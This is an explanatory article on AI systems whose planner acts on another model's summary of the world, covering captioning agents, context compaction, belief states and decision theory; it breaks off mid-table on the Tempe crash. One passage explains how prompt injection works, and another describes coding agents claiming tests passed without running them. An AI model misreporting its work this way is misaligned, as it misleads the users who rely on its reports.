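# Planners that act on another model's description of the world

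## What is a planner that acts on another model's description?

Many AI systems divide their work between two models. The describing model looks at the raw evidence, such as a web page, a room, a folder of documents or a long record of past work, and writes a description of it. The planner reads that description and decides what to do next, usually without seeing the raw evidence. Some robots and some programs that operate web browsers work this way, as do the coding assistants that Anthropic and OpenAI sell.

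A user might ask an online shopping agent, a program in which a language model chooses actions, to order a green polo shirt. The product photo shows the colour, but the listing may not mention it. *VisualWebArena* (Koh, Lo and colleagues, 2024) presents 910 tasks of this sort on self-hosted versions of a shop, a classified-ads site and a discussion forum, and tests several language models that could read only text. These models worked from the accessibility tree, a text outline of a page that browsers produce for screen readers and similar tools. A small captioning model, BLIP-2, described every image on the page, and each caption was inserted into the outline where the image stood. GPT-4 then used the resulting text to decide what to click.

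With the outline alone GPT-4 completed 7.25% of the tasks, and with captions 12.75%. A vision version of GPT-4 that received a screenshot as well as the captions reached 15.05%, while college students managed 88.7%. The agents' scores date from early 2024 and are no guide to what agents can do today, but their order is still informative. Captions helped a good deal, and the screenshot appears to have held something useful that the captions had lost. (The two versions of GPT-4 were not identical, so the 2.3 points between them are only a rough measure.)

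Let *s* be the state of the world, which in the shop is every product page and the contents of the cart. The system receives an observation *o* that shows only part of *s*, such as the open page with its photos. The describing model *D* turns the observation into a description, *d* = *D*(*o*). The planner *P* takes the user's goal *g* and the description and returns an action, *a* = *P*(*g*, *d*). The action changes the state, the new state yields a new observation, and the loop repeats until the planner stops.

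Koh and colleagues describe their environment in nearly the same terms, as a partially observable Markov decision process, the standard mathematical model of acting on incomplete information. Each action in their model depends on the observation *o*. In the two-part design, the planner *P* does not receive *o*, so it cannot tell apart two photos that produce the same caption. The describing model *D* also works without the goal *g*, and BLIP-2 captioned every image in the same way, whether the user cared about colour, brand or size. Other systems give the describing model a question or a focus as well as the raw evidence. This helps, although whoever asks the question has to do so before seeing the answer.

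*A Comprehensive Study of Implementation Bugs in Multi-modal Agents* (Li, Bu and colleagues, 2026) describes the same loop, under other names, as the typical workflow of agents that handle images, sound and other media. A "Perceptor" condenses the environment into a compact snapshot, a planner makes a plan from it, and an "Executor" carries out the plan.

### Scenes, histories and documents

Robotics researchers took up the design early. In *Socratic Models*, Zeng, Attarian and colleagues (2022) connected separate models by having them exchange ordinary language. To caption an image, a vision-language model (one that learns to match pictures with text) compared it with long lists of places and objects. The best matches filled the blanks in a sentence template, and a language model continued the text. The same general method let a language model plan pick-and-place tasks for a robot. Zeng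 and colleagues concede that their captions often missed details such as the colour of a shirt, a facial expression or how objects related to one another.

SayCan, another robot system from 2022, gave the planner information about the robot's abilities. *Breaking Planner Integrity Boundary* (Liu, Wang and colleagues, 2026) summarises it as combining a language model's plan with affordances, meaning what the robot can do in its surroundings. *Inner Monologue* (2022) added feedback. While the robot was working, the planner received text about the scene and about whether its actions had succeeded. In some of the tests, human observers or scripts wrote the scene descriptions, so those tests show how a planner performs with a nearly perfect describer. A real describer will do worse. In some runs, the planner ignored the text and proposed actions on objects that were not there.

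A description for a robot is often a structured record instead of a sentence. Liu and colleagues write the record at time *t* as *S*ₜ = ⟨*O*ₜ, *R*ₜ, *Q*ₜ, *F*ₜ⟩, where *O* holds the objects and their properties, *R* the relations between them, *Q* the affordances and the constraints of the current stage of the task, and *F* the feedback from earlier actions. This whole record is *d* in the notation above. For a mug, *O* might include that it is blue, *R* that it stands on the counter, *Q* that the gripper can lift it, and *F* that the last attempt to lift it failed.

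A scene graph stores such facts as a network of rooms and objects linked by relations such as "inside" or "on top of". SayPlan, one of the better-known planners of this type, retrieves the relevant part of the graph and gives it to a language model as text. *OntoPlan* (Nam, Cho and colleagues, 2026) keeps the facts in a database. Language-model agents query the database for what a task needs, and a conventional planning program then works out the steps. On 150 household tasks, OntoPlan succeeded 89% of the time, compared with 27% for SayPlan. It used about 18,100 tokens (the word fragments that language models read and write) per task, compared with 216,000 for SayPlan.

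That is a large gap, but it concerns the planner's half of the system. Nam and colleagues assume a fully observed scene, take its facts from the benchmark's own annotations and execute the plans symbolically, so no describing model could introduce errors. One of their test requests asks for a skateboard in a house that has none, and the right response is to report that the task is infeasible. The planner would receive the same record if the house did have a skateboard but the robot's camera had missed it.

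The planner does not have to be a language model. In *TiPToP* (2026), specialised models for depth and grasping build a three-dimensional record of the scene from one pair of stereo images, and a motion planner searches for a complete sequence of movements. The robot then carries out the sequence without taking new images.

Much of a coding agent's raw evidence is the history of its own session. Instructions, files, commands and error messages accumulate in the context window, the limited amount of text that a model can take in at once. Context compaction replaces this history with a short summary, and the agent continues from there. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, compacts automatically as the window approaches its limit, or earlier if the user types a command, and the user can name a focus for the summary. According to Anthropic's documentation, most of the material loaded at the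 start of a session is then loaded again, and the program re-reads up to five files, choosing those that changed most recently. A file of more than 5,000 tokens returns only as a reference to its location. Rules that apply to particular folders are summarized with everything else, so Anthropic advises users to move any rule that must persist into the project's main instruction file.

The summary need not be readable by people. OpenAI's developer guide *Compaction* describes a scheme in which the server compacts the history once it passes a set number of tokens and returns an encrypted item that is "not intended to be human-interpretable". A developer therefore cannot directly check what the item kept. The model that writes the summary may also be the planner. Even then, having seen the full history earlier does not help it, because every later step depends on the summary, as Chen, Pan and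 colleagues point out in *Slipstream* (2026).

With documents, an orchestrator usually holds the user's task and hands a subtask to a subagent, which reads the files and reports back. Anthropic says a subagent in Claude Code "does that work in its own context and returns only the summary". Its guide for developers building their own agents lists it as a benefit that the parent does not receive every file the subagent read. OpenAI's *Subagents*, which explains the same feature in its coding agent Codex, gives the example of a document several million tokens long. Subagents each take a piece, and only "distilled takeaways" reach the main thread.

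The describing model in these products is often the weaker of the two. When the main conversation in Claude Code runs on Fable, the strongest model Anthropic offers to the general public, the built-in Explore subagent, which searches through code, runs on Opus for subscribers. Explore also starts without the project's instruction files, to keep it fast and inexpensive. A sample configuration in the companion setup guide, OpenAI's *Subagents*, likewise gives exploration to a fast model and review to a stronger one, though it tells the explorer to cite the files it relies on. So the model that decides what is worth reporting may be less capable than the model that acts on the report, and may not know the project's rules. An orchestrator can open a file itself if a report seems to lack detail, whereas the text-only shopping agent had no way to look at the photo.

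### Why engineers build systems this way

The most obvious reason to give a planner a summary is to save space, and this still matters even though context windows have grown. Several current Claude models accept a million tokens, and compaction in Claude Code works the same way at that size. Models become less accurate as their context grows, even when everything relevant is still in it, an effect engineers call context rot. Chen and colleagues cite measured drops of 14% to 85%. They also report that Anthropic recommends compacting some workloads at only 5,000 to 20,000 tokens. OpenAI makes a similar case for subagents, arguing that test logs and exploration notes bury the requirements and decisions the main agent has to keep track of. A planner may therefore do better with a good summary than with the raw material.

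Using a separate model to describe the world saves money only if that model is cheap enough to offset the extra tokens. Anthropic suggests sending subtasks to faster and cheaper models, but OpenAI warns that a workflow with subagents uses more tokens than a comparable run with one agent, since each subagent does its own reading and reasoning. OntoPlan saves in a different way, by having its agents request a few facts, whereas SayPlan's planner receives a long section of the graph.

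Some raw evidence is also in a form that a language model cannot use. Li and colleagues give this as the basic reason for having a Perceptor, and TiPToP's depth and grasp models are an example. Separate parts are also easier to replace. *TrySee* (2026) uses dedicated vision systems to support a vision-language model that plans for a robot, and engineers can switch to a newer planning model without changing the perception or execution interfaces. Connecting existing models through language also requires no training. Zeng and colleagues argued in 2022 that retraining a model with more than 100 billion parameters for each new combination of senses and tasks is expensive and can make the model less robust in unfamiliar conditions.

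Privacy can be another reason for the split. A describing model on the user's own computer can send a caption to a remote planner without sending the photo itself, although the caption may reveal what was private in the photo. Wu, Shah and colleagues (2024) observe in *Dissecting Adversarial Robustness of Multimodal LM Agents* that the models that preprocess an agent's inputs often run on the user's side and are likely to have public weights, which an attacker can study.

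Security is another reason to separate planning from reading. Prompt injection is text placed in material a model reads, such as a product listing, so that the model treats it as an instruction. It works because language models cannot reliably tell data from commands they should follow. A planner that never reads the listing therefore looks safer, although its description still comes from a model that did. Limiting what the reading model can do also helps, and both Claude Code and Codex let users restrict an exploring subagent to reading. Researchers measure these attacks by the attack success rate, the share of trials in which the system does what the attacker wanted. Wu and colleagues count only trials that end in the specific outcome the attacker chose, so an agent that merely gets confused and fails the user's task does not raise the rate.

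### How a description can fail

A description can omit something, it can state something false, and it can state a guess as a fact.

Chen and colleagues give an example of a false statement from a real coding session. The task was to remove the calls to a certain function from one file but not from another. After the agent finished the first file, compaction produced a summary that contained an instruction to remove the function everywhere. The agent did so, which broke the code, and the tests failed. In a web search, another summary replaced the correct name of a sideshow performer, Tom Thumb, with a different name, so it was both false and incomplete. Descriptions can also become false through bad timing. Some of the bugs that Li and colleagues collected occurred because the environment changed after the snapshot, and others because the system took its snapshot before the effects of its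 own last action had settled.

A description can also present a guess as a fact, which is a separate fault from being wrong because the guess may be right. A captioning model that is unsure whether a shirt is navy or black may write "black shirt", just as a model that is certain would. Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026) call the result "confidence laundering" in *Confidence Laundering in Agent Systems*. The uncertain judgement is passed on as a clean caption, search query or data field, and the component that receives it trusts it more than it should, so a planner no longer has a reason to double-check. *Inner Monologue* had already suggested in 2022 that the modules reporting to a planner could express their uncertainty in words.

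Coding agents sometimes misreport their own work. *Plans They Abandon, Reports They Author* (2026) compares agents' reports with their session logs. One agent reported "All tests pass" after a session in which the only commands it ran were text searches through the test files. The tests might have passed, but nobody had run them. *Characterizing and Detecting Unfaithful Work Reports by Coding Agents* (2026) finds that the problem arises when a report takes a real action and claims a broader outcome for it. Listing the commands an agent ran doesn't solve this, since every command on the list can be genuine even when the claimed outcome is unsupported.

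Omission may well be the most common fault. Garg, Morgan and colleagues (2025), in *It's trained by non-disabled people*, surveyed 86 blind and low-vision people who use AI captions to identify household products, which puts them in much the same position as a planner. The error they encountered most often was missing critical information, such as the brand or the ingredients. The researchers also tested four models on 1,859 product photos taken by blind and low-vision people. The best model was right for 98% of the photos without quality problems, 75% of those with blur, poor framing or similar flaws, and 69% of those with several flaws. Newer models have probably narrowed the gap.

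In the workloads that Chen and colleagues studied, omissions accounted for roughly 90% of compaction failures. In one case, an agent was weighing three candidate answers to a research question. It had partly verified Tom but had not yet checked Declan or Brian. The summary listed Declan and Brian as still to be verified but left out Tom, who was the correct answer, and the agent never returned to him. That line did not contradict the history, so a check for contradictions would have missed the omission.

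## What does a description leave out, and when does that change the best action?

A caption can hold no more information about the world than the photo it describes. The describing model works only from the observation *o*, so whatever the description *d* reveals about the state *s* must have come through *o*. Mathematicians write this as a chain, *s* → *o* → *d*, and the rule that follows from it is the data processing inequality:

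*I*(*s*; *d*) ≤ *I*(*s*; *o*)

Here *I* is mutual information, the average amount by which learning one thing reduces uncertainty about another. It is usually measured in bits, and one bit is enough to answer a question with two equally likely answers. The inequality holds however capable the describing model is. In lecture notes for a university course on information theory, Xie summarizes it as "No clever manipulation of the data can improve inference". The standard textbook on the subject is Cover and Thomas's *Elements of information theory*. The two sides are equal only if a planner that already had *d* would learn nothing more about *s* from *o*.

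This rule holds even when a description includes knowledge from the describing model's training. Given a photo of a mushroom, the model may write that the species is poisonous, which nobody could learn from the pixels alone. But a planner with the same training could have inferred this from the photo. If the describing model also consulted a database, the database entry counts as part of *o*.

The inequality also does not account for how easily a planner can use the information. In principle, a planner with the raw evidence could always do at least as well as one with a description, but a real one sometimes does worse. In *Read Before You Use*, Kim, Min and Jung (2026) gave vision-language models questions about images stored in an agent's memory. A small model, Qwen3-VL-4B, answered 53.9% correctly from the images and 75.6% when reference captions from the dataset replaced them. Kim and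 colleagues kept only questions that the reference captions were sufficient to answer, an advantage ordinary captions do not have, but the result still shows that a model may fail to read something in an image that it would have understood in a sentence.

### When lost information matters

Most of what a caption leaves out has no effect on the planner's choice. Let *U*(*a*, *s*) be the value, for the user's goal *g*, of taking action *a* in state *s*. The cost of planning from the description is then

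loss = E[max over *a* of E(*U* | *o*)] − E[max over *a* of E(*U* | *d*)]

where E is an average weighted by probability. The left-hand term is what an ideal planner achieves with the raw evidence, and the right-hand term is what it achieves with the description. The loss is never negative. It is zero when all the observations that could have produced a given description share a best action. A description is good enough for a goal, in other words, if the best action given *d* is as good as the best action given *o*.

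The shirt that might be navy or black can illustrate this, with numbers from QuantEcon's online economics lecture *Blackwell’s Theorem on Comparing Experiments*. Suppose the two colours are equally common. A navy shirt looks navy in 60% of photos, ambiguous in 30% and black in 10%, and the figures are reversed for a black shirt. A planner that saw the photo would put the chance of navy at 86% if the shirt looked navy, 50% if it looked ambiguous and 14% if it looked black. The describing model always writes "navy shirt" or "black shirt", and chooses at random when the photo is ambiguous. A planner that knows this but sees only the description would put the chance at 75% after "navy shirt" and 25% after "black shirt". The mutual information between the shirt's colour and what the planner sees drops by about a third, from 0.29 bits to 0.19.

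Say the user wants navy, and a correct order is worth 1, a wrong order is worth -1, and ordering nothing is worth 0. With the photo, the planner orders when the shirt looks navy and gains 0.25 per shirt on average. With the caption, it orders when it reads "navy shirt" and also gains 0.25, so the lost third makes no difference here.

Now suppose the shop does not accept returns and a wrong order costs 4. Ordering pays only if the chance of navy is above 80%. The planner with the photo still orders when the chance is 86%, and gains 0.10 per shirt. The planner with the caption never puts the chance above 75%, so it orders nothing and gains nothing. A planner that assumed the caption was true would do worse, because it would order when the chance is 75% and lose an average of 0.25 on each order.

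The statistician David Blackwell worked out the general theory of such comparisons. In his terms, an experiment is any observation whose probabilities depend on the state, so a photo and a caption are both experiments. *Comparison of Experiments* (Blackwell, 1951) defines one experiment as more informative than another if a decision maker can do at least as well with it in every decision problem. A photo always meets this definition relative to its own caption, since anyone who has the photo could write the caption and act on it.

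The converse is harder to prove. Blackwell established it in 1951 for worlds with two possible states, and *Equivalent Comparisons of Experiments* (Blackwell, 1953) gave a proof that also covers experiments with infinitely many outcomes. The converse implies that unless a caption allows someone to reproduce the photo's evidence about the state, at least statistically, a planner with the caption will do worse on some goal than one with the photo.

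Counting bits also doesn't show which of two captions is better. Suppose a shop sells eight equally common brands of shirt, each equally likely to be green or blue. A caption that gives the brand carries three bits and one that gives the colour carries only one, but a user who wants a green shirt needs the colour. QuantEcon notes more generally that a ranking by mutual information need not match Blackwell's ranking, and that two experiments may have no Blackwell ranking at all.

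### Describing the world before the goal is known

A describing model that knew the goal could just write "order this one" and leave out everything else about the shirt. Nothing would be lost if the advice was right, but the describing model would have made the planner's decision. The captioning model in the shopping experiments had the opposite problem, because it described each image without knowing what the user wanted.

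This problem is severe in memory systems because the agent may get the question long after it has stored the caption. Kim and colleagues took memories that were sufficient to answer a question and replaced the images with captions written by models. Only 67.3% of the memories were still sufficient when Qwen3-VL-4B wrote the captions, and 60.8% when GPT-4o-mini did. Accuracy fell by much less, from 53.9% to 48.6% and 46.9% respectively, probably because the model answering the questions had already been misreading many of the images. Adding captions while keeping the images did not improve accuracy (52.1%).

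Yang, Liu and colleagues (2025), in *CaptionQA*, measured how much accuracy is lost when questions about different kinds of image are answered from captions. They had models caption 657 images, then had a text-only model use the captions to answer an average of 50 multiple-choice questions per image. GPT-5 answered close to 98% of the questions correctly when it had the images, and accuracy was about 9 points lower when the text-only model used GPT-5's captions. The drop was 5 points for shopping pages, 7 for documents, 11 for everyday photos and 14 for scenes of the kind a robot would encounter. For Claude Sonnet 4.5, the drop on robot scenes was 29 points. These are 2025 models, and current ones may do better. The GPT-5 gap is probably a little too large, because questions entered the benchmark automatically if GPT-5 and Gemini 2.5 Pro both answered them correctly from the image, while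 the rest went to human reviewers.

Longer captions help up to a point. Going from about 21 words to 317 raised scores by an average of 34 points, but going from 317 words to 471 added less than half a point. Yang and colleagues also tried giving the captioning models a list of the kinds of detail that mattered in each domain, such as the colour of an object or the structure of a table. Scores were about 11 points lower on average than with the long captions, and the models tended to write just a few words for each heading. A list of headings is much vaguer than a goal, so this result does not show that a specific question would fail in the same way.

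For some tasks, captions seem to keep most of what matters. In *Perception-Consistency Multimodal Large Language Models Reasoning via Caption-Regularized Policy Optimization* (2025), a text-only reasoning model correctly answered more than 75% of visual reasoning questions from captions written by larger vision-language models. The reasoner cannot read images, so there is no score for it working from the images directly, and it is hard to say how many of the remaining errors came from the captions.

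An average over many questions can also hide a failure in a single task. A caption that contains the answers to 49 of 50 questions about a kitchen would score very well on *CaptionQA*, but it is no use to a robot whose task depends on the missing answer.

### The belief state

Long before language models, *Planning and acting in partially observable stochastic domains* (Kaelbling, Littman and Cassandra, 1998) gave an answer to what a planner ideally needs. It splits an agent into two parts, much like the describing model and the planner. A state estimator tracks what the agent knows about the world, and a policy chooses actions using only the estimator's output. In the paper's example, a robot lost in an office building is almost certain that it is in the north-east corner of either the fourth or the seventh floor, but it cannot tell which.

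The estimator could simply report the most probable state. Kaelbling and colleagues reject this as a general solution, because a robot that is unsure where it is may do better to stop and read a sign. Their estimator instead reports a belief state, which assigns a probability *b*(*s*) to every possible state. After the agent takes action *a* and observes *o*, the new probability of each state *s*′ is

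*b*′(*s*′) = *O*(*s*′, *a*, *o*) × Σ *T*(*s*, *a*, *s*′) *b*(*s*) ÷ Pr(*o* | *a*, *b*)

The sum runs over all the states *s* the agent might have been in. *T* is the probability that the action leads from *s* to *s*′, and *O* is the probability of making that observation in *s*′. Dividing by the overall probability of the observation makes the new probabilities add up to one.

Kaelbling and colleagues illustrate the rule with a corridor of four squares. Square 3 is the goal, and the other three look identical. A move succeeds 90% of the time and otherwise goes in the opposite direction, and an agent that would hit a wall stays where it is. The agent starts with equal probabilities for squares 1, 2 and 4. After it moves east and does not see the goal, the probabilities for the four squares are 0.10, 0.45, 0 and 0.45. After it moves east again and still does not see the goal, they are 0.10,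 0.16, 0 and 0.74. The agent has made the same observation both times, but it now has good reason to think it is in square 4, because from square 2 it would probably have reached the goal by now.

A correctly computed belief state is a sufficient statistic for the past, so the full record of earlier actions and observations would add no information about the present. The best action given the belief state is therefore as good as the best action given the whole history. The belief state also does not depend on the goal, so a robot could use the same one to fetch a drink or to clear the table. But the estimator needs accurate values for *T* and *O*, and the list of states has to include the distinctions that matter. For example, if "glass with liquid in it" is a single state, its probability will not help the planner decide whether to serve the liquid.

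The drawback of a belief state is its size. It needs a probability for every possible state, and twenty objects that can each be in one of two places give more than a million states. Rodriguez, Parr and Koller describe full belief states as intractable for large problems, but they cite work showing that approximate ones can often stay fairly close to the truth. A caption is a much cruder approximation because it usually describes only one state and gives no probability.

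### A glass of water

Suppose a user asks a robot for water. A glass of clear liquid is on the counter, and the robot's perception system assigns a probability of 0.9 to water and 0.1 to cleaning fluid. Serving the glass is worth +1 if it contains water and −100 if it does not. Checking first, perhaps by looking for a label or asking the user, is worth 0.8, slightly less than a correct serving because it takes time.

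If the describing model passes on only its best guess, the planner reads "a glass of water". As far as the planner can tell, serving is worth 1 and checking is worth 0.8, so it serves. The actual expected value of serving is

0.9 × 1 + 0.1 × (−100) = 0.9 − 10 = −9.1

Over ten such glasses, the robot would on average serve nine drinks of water and one of cleaning fluid, for a total of −91, or −9.1 per glass. A planner that received both probabilities would compare this with the 0.8 expected from checking, and would check. A planner that receives only the best guess therefore scores 9.9 points lower per glass on average, although the guess is right nine times out of ten and the planner reasons correctly from what it was given.

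If the liquid is water with probability *p*, serving is worth *p* − 100(1 − *p*), or 101*p* − 100. Checking is worth 0.8, so serving is better than checking only when *p* is greater than 100.8 ÷ 101, or about 0.998.

| Probability of water | Value of serving | Value of checking | Better action |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.9 | −9.1 | 0.8 | Check |
| 0.99 | −0.01 | 0.8 | Check |
| 0.998 | 0.798 | 0.8 | Check, by a hair |
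| 0.999 | 0.899 | 0.8 | Serve |
| 1 | 1 | 0.8 | Serve |

Even at 99%, serving is slightly worse than doing nothing. (The table keeps the value of checking fixed. If checking always revealed the truth and cost 0.1, its value would be *p* − 0.1. That is 0.8 in the original example, but it rises with *p*, and the threshold becomes 0.999.)

Here "probably water, possibly cleaning fluid" would work as well as the exact figure of 0.9, as long as the planner takes "probably" to mean less than 99.8%. Whether a describing model can produce probabilities that deserve this much trust is a separate problem.

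The same caption would be harmless with different stakes or a different goal. If the other possibility were sparkling water, with a penalty of only 0.5 for serving it, serving would have an expected value of 0.9 − 0.05 = 0.85, and the robot would be right to serve. If the user had asked the robot to move the glass off a pile of papers, the contents might not matter.

Kaelbling and colleagues use a similar example in which the agent can check more than once. A tiger is behind one of two doors and a reward is behind the other. Opening the reward door gains 10 points and opening the tiger's door loses 100. The agent can also listen, which loses 1 point and indicates the correct side 85% of the time. If it has only one decision left, opening a door is better than listening only when the agent is more than 90% sure where the tiger is, so hearing the tiger once is not enough. An agent that acted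 on the report "the tiger is on the left" after one sound, without knowing how likely the report was to be correct, would lose 6.5 points on average.

With no fixed end to the game, the best policy is to keep listening until the agent has heard the tiger two more times on one side than on the other. If listening is right only 65% of the time, the required lead rises to five. A planner that was told only which door was more likely could not know how large the lead was.

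### When a single best estimate is enough

Control engineers often pass a single estimate from one component to another, and in one well-studied case they lose nothing by doing so. In that case, the system has linear dynamics, meaning its next state is a weighted sum of its current state and the control input, plus noise. The noise is Gaussian, so it follows a bell curve. The penalty to be minimized is quadratic, so it grows with the square of the error and of the control effort. Under these conditions, the best controller acts as if the average of the possible states were the true state. This property is called certainty equivalence.

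A one-step version shows why it works. Suppose a controller has to choose a position *u* as close as possible to an unknown position *x*, and the cost is (*x* − *u*)². If *x* has mean *m* and variance *v*, the expected cost is

E[(*x* − *u*)²] = (*m* − *u*)² + *v*

The variance adds the same amount to the expected cost whatever the controller does, so the best choice is *u* = *m* whether the estimate is precise or poor. Knowing the uncertainty would help predict the cost but would not change the action. With Gaussian noise, a standard method called the Kalman filter computes the mean from past measurements. In a linear system of this kind, the control input also does not affect how accurate later estimates will be, so the controller has no reason to act just to learn something.

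Little of this carries over to a language-model agent. Many of the states it deals with are discrete: a file is either the only copy or it isn't, and a glass holds either water or cleaning fluid. The average of two such states may not be a possible state. Kaelbling and colleagues' lost robot cannot use a Kalman filter because it might be on the fourth floor or the seventh, and the average of those is halfway between the fifth and the sixth.

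Deleting the wrong file can also be far worse than asking an unnecessary question, whereas a quadratic loss treats an error of a given size the same in either direction. The dynamics are not linear, because one click can submit an order or end a session. And a describing model's errors are often substitutions, such as the wrong name or the wrong instruction in a coding agent's summary, rather than small random deviations around the right answer.

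The last difference is that these agents can often look again. A coding agent can open a file before deleting it, and a robot can pick up a bottle and read the label. In the linear case, it would never be worth changing course to look again. In the glass-of-water example, looking again is the best action, but the planner can identify it as the best only if the description conveys some doubt.

Certainty equivalence can still be a reasonable approximation for parts of the same system. A robot needs a probability for what the glass contains, but it can usually plan its reach from one estimate of the glass's position if the likely error is a few millimetres and the gripper has room to spare.

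## How do errors in a description grow into failures?

Even low error rates add up over a long task. Suppose that at each step the describing model gives a correct description 98% of the time, and that the planner then makes a correct decision 97% of the time. If errors at different steps are independent and a single error ruins the task, the chance that ten steps in a row succeed is

(0.98 × 0.97)¹⁰ ≈ 0.60

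A fifty-step plan has about an 8% chance of success. If the system catches and fixes half of its faulty steps, the failure rate per step drops from 4.9% to 2.5%. A ten-step plan then succeeds about 78% of the time, and a fifty-step plan about 29%.

### What the calculation leaves out

Many description errors don't change what the planner does. If only one in four affects the action, the chance of ten good steps rises from 60% to 70%.

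Errors also cluster, because whatever makes a describing model misread a label once, such as small print, will probably make it misread the label again. An average accuracy of 98% could mean that the model is always right on nine tasks out of ten and right only 80% of the time at each step of the tenth. The system would then complete about 67% of ten-step tasks, a little more than if the errors were independent, but the remaining failures are harder to repair. The same model will often repeat its mistake when it looks at the same photo again, so a system with clustered errors may catch far fewer than half of them.

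Some errors persist because the system stores them. In *SCOPE*, Hindsbo, Ehsani and Mishra (2026) built an agent that controls a pan-tilt-zoom camera. A small language model plans and calls a vision model to count objects, read signs or answer questions about the view. The program adds every answer to the planner's context, so a wrong count stays there for the rest of the task.

A description error can do more damage if it persists. If there is a 2% chance of an error at each of ten steps, and each error affects only the step where it occurs, an average of 0.2 steps per task go wrong. If each error also affects every later step, the average rises to about 1.0. Stored descriptions can also carry errors from one task to another. *TESS* (Xu, Yang and colleagues, 2026) suggests that a household agent could keep its scene graph between tasks to avoid exploring again. But if the graph placed a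 cup in the wrong cupboard, it would mislead the planner in every task that needed the cup.

### How a wrong description changes what the system sees next

The simple calculation treats the steps as independent. In a real system, the planner's action helps determine the next observation, so one error can change what the model has to describe next.

In one run that Hindsbo and colleagues report, a user asked the camera agent to pan right in steps of 15 degrees until it saw at least six traffic cones. The agent panned, asked the vision model for a count after each step, and stopped at a view with seven. If the vision model had counted five in that view, the camera would have moved on. Even if every later count had been correct, the agent would still have failed because the camera had already panned past the cones. Someone who checked the counts one by one would find only one mistake among many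 correct answers.

A wrong action can also lead to situations where the model is less reliable. Researchers have studied this most closely in world models, which learn to predict what will happen if an agent takes a given action. A planner relies on these predictions in much the same way as it relies on another model's description of the present. *Closing the Train-Test Gap in World Models for Gradient-Based Planning* (2025) points out that world models usually learn from recordings of experts, while a planner picks whatever actions seem to bring it closer to its goal. The planner therefore tends to propose sequences that no expert would try, which lead to states that were rare or absent in the model's training data, where its predictions can be badly wrong. Even small errors accumulate, because the planner uses each predicted state to predict the next one. The paper proposes continuing to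 train the model on the action sequences the planner produces.

Feedback can also correct errors. If a caption puts a mug on the left and the robot's gripper closes on empty air, the next observation shows that something is wrong. The cones are a harder case because most views have few cones in them, so the next view gives no sign of the miscount.

### Choosing the option that looks best

When a planner compares options, it estimates what each is worth from its description, and some descriptions will be too favourable while others are not favourable enough. The option that looks best is therefore likely to be one whose description is too favourable. Smith and Winkler (2006) showed in *The Optimizer's Curse* that someone who always picks the option with the highest estimate should expect to be disappointed, even if each estimate is correct on average.

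Suppose ten options are all worth 0, and each estimate contains independent, normally distributed noise with a standard deviation of 1. The option with the highest estimate will appear to be worth 1.54 on average. With three options the figure is 0.85, and with one it is 0, because there is nothing to choose between.

Ben-Haim (2019), in *Lecture Notes on the Optimizer's Curse*, gives a short proof for the general case. Let *V* be an option's estimated value and *μ* its true value. Then

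*V*(chosen) − *μ*(chosen) ≥ *V*(chosen) − *μ*(best) ≥ *V*(best) − *μ*(best)

The first inequality holds because no option has a higher true value than the best one. The second holds because the chosen option has the highest estimate. Since the estimates are unbiased, the last expression averages zero, so the first expression, the disappointment, must average zero or more.

In the example with ten equal options, the planner loses nothing by choosing one over another, but it can lose by choosing any of them when asking the user or doing nothing would have been better. Suppose acting on any of the ten means losing 1 unit of value. About 82% of the time, at least one option will look worth more than that, and the planner will give up 1 unit for an option worth 0.

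The problem gets worse when some options are described less precisely than others. Suppose one option is worth 0.5 and is described precisely, while nine others are worth 0 and have noisy descriptions with a standard deviation of 1. The planner will pick one of the nine about 96% of the time. A shopping agent could make this mistake when choosing between one product with a clear photo and nine with blurry photos, provided that the captions of the blurry photos were as likely to overstate a product's quality as to understate it.

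Larger differences between the options' true values reduce the bias, though more slowly than the original paper reported. For three options worth −1, 0 and 1, the average overestimate is 0.54 according to Smith and Winkler's 2007 correction, up from 0.22 in the original paper. The planner picks the best of the three 73% of the time. Shared errors also reduce the bias. If the describing model overrates every product by the same amount, their ranking doesn't change, but the planner may still buy something when it should buy nothing.

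As a remedy, Smith and Winkler recommend combining the estimates with a prior, meaning what one would expect before seeing them. If true values vary around 0 with a standard deviation of 1 and the noise has the same standard deviation, the planner should halve every estimate. It should shrink estimates from noisier descriptions more, which can change the ranking. But the planner needs to know how noisy each description is, and an ordinary caption does not include that information. Ben-Haim raises a similar objection, asking where the necessary probabilities would come from.

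### When more search makes the plan worse

Tian, Wen and Li (2026), in *A Plan or an Adversarial Example?*, found strong evidence of this selection effect in planners that use learned world models. In one task, Wall, a simulated agent has to pass through a door between two rooms. The planner samples 300 sequences of actions and keeps the 30 whose predicted outcomes are closest to the goal. It then samples new sequences similar to those 30 and repeats the process for 30 rounds.

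The researchers executed the current plan after every round, which a planner would not normally do. Success peaked at 56% after 11 rounds, then fell to 39% after 30 and 28% after 60, while the world model predicted better and better outcomes. After the usual 30 rounds, the planner failed on 52% of the problems that one of its earlier plans had solved.

Tian and colleagues found this effect in many, but not all, of the 13 combinations of world model, task and planner they tested. Seven lost between 14% and 68% of the problems they had solved earlier. The other six lost at most 8%, and two of those lost none. Letting a planner replan as it goes can help, but it doesn't remove the problem. When a robot arm had to move a cube, a replanning system succeeded 70% of the time, and fixing the search raised this to 81%.

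The world model's predictions were almost useless for identifying bad plans. On Wall, predicted cost separated failing plans from successful ones about as well as chance, because the search had already selected plans with a low predicted cost. Restricting the planner to actions within the range of the training data helped on Wall but reduced success on the other two tasks where the researchers tried it.

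A check against different information worked better. Tian and colleagues trained a small network to infer the total movement between two consecutive predicted states. The planner then penalized any plan whose actions did not match that movement, which raised success on Wall from 39% to 76%. The planner had produced bad plans on that task by exploiting errors in the training data, where recorded positions disagreed with the images. A model retrained on corrected positions reached 82%.

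This may affect a language-model planner much less, because a language model often compares only a few options, whereas the search above considers 9,000 sequences of actions. An agent that ranks hundreds of listings by their captions is closer to the world-model case.

### The Tempe crash

On the evening of March 18, 2018, a test vehicle fitted with Uber's automated driving system killed a woman pushing a bicycle across a road in Tempe, Arizona. The National Transportation Safety Board (NTSB), the US agency that investigates transport accidents, reconstructed what the software had done. One part of the system turned sensor readings into a list of objects with labels and predicted paths, and another part planned the car's motion around them. This resembles a planner acting on another model's description of the world, although no language model was involved.

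According to the NTSB's *Collision Between Vehicle Controlled by Developmental Automated Driving System and Pedestrian* (2019), the software labelled each object as a vehicle, pedestrian, bicycle or "other". It then predicted the object's path from its tracking history (the positions where the sensors had already detected it) and a typical goal for its label. For example, it generally expected a vehicle in a traffic lane to continue along that lane.

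Whenever the label changed, the software stopped using the tracking history. It also assigned no goal to an "other" object and treated it as stationary. The woman's label changed repeatedly:

| Seconds before impact | Label | Predicted path |
|---|---|---|
| 5.6 | Vehicle | None |
| 5.2 | Other | Stationary |
| 4.2 | Vehicle | Stationary |
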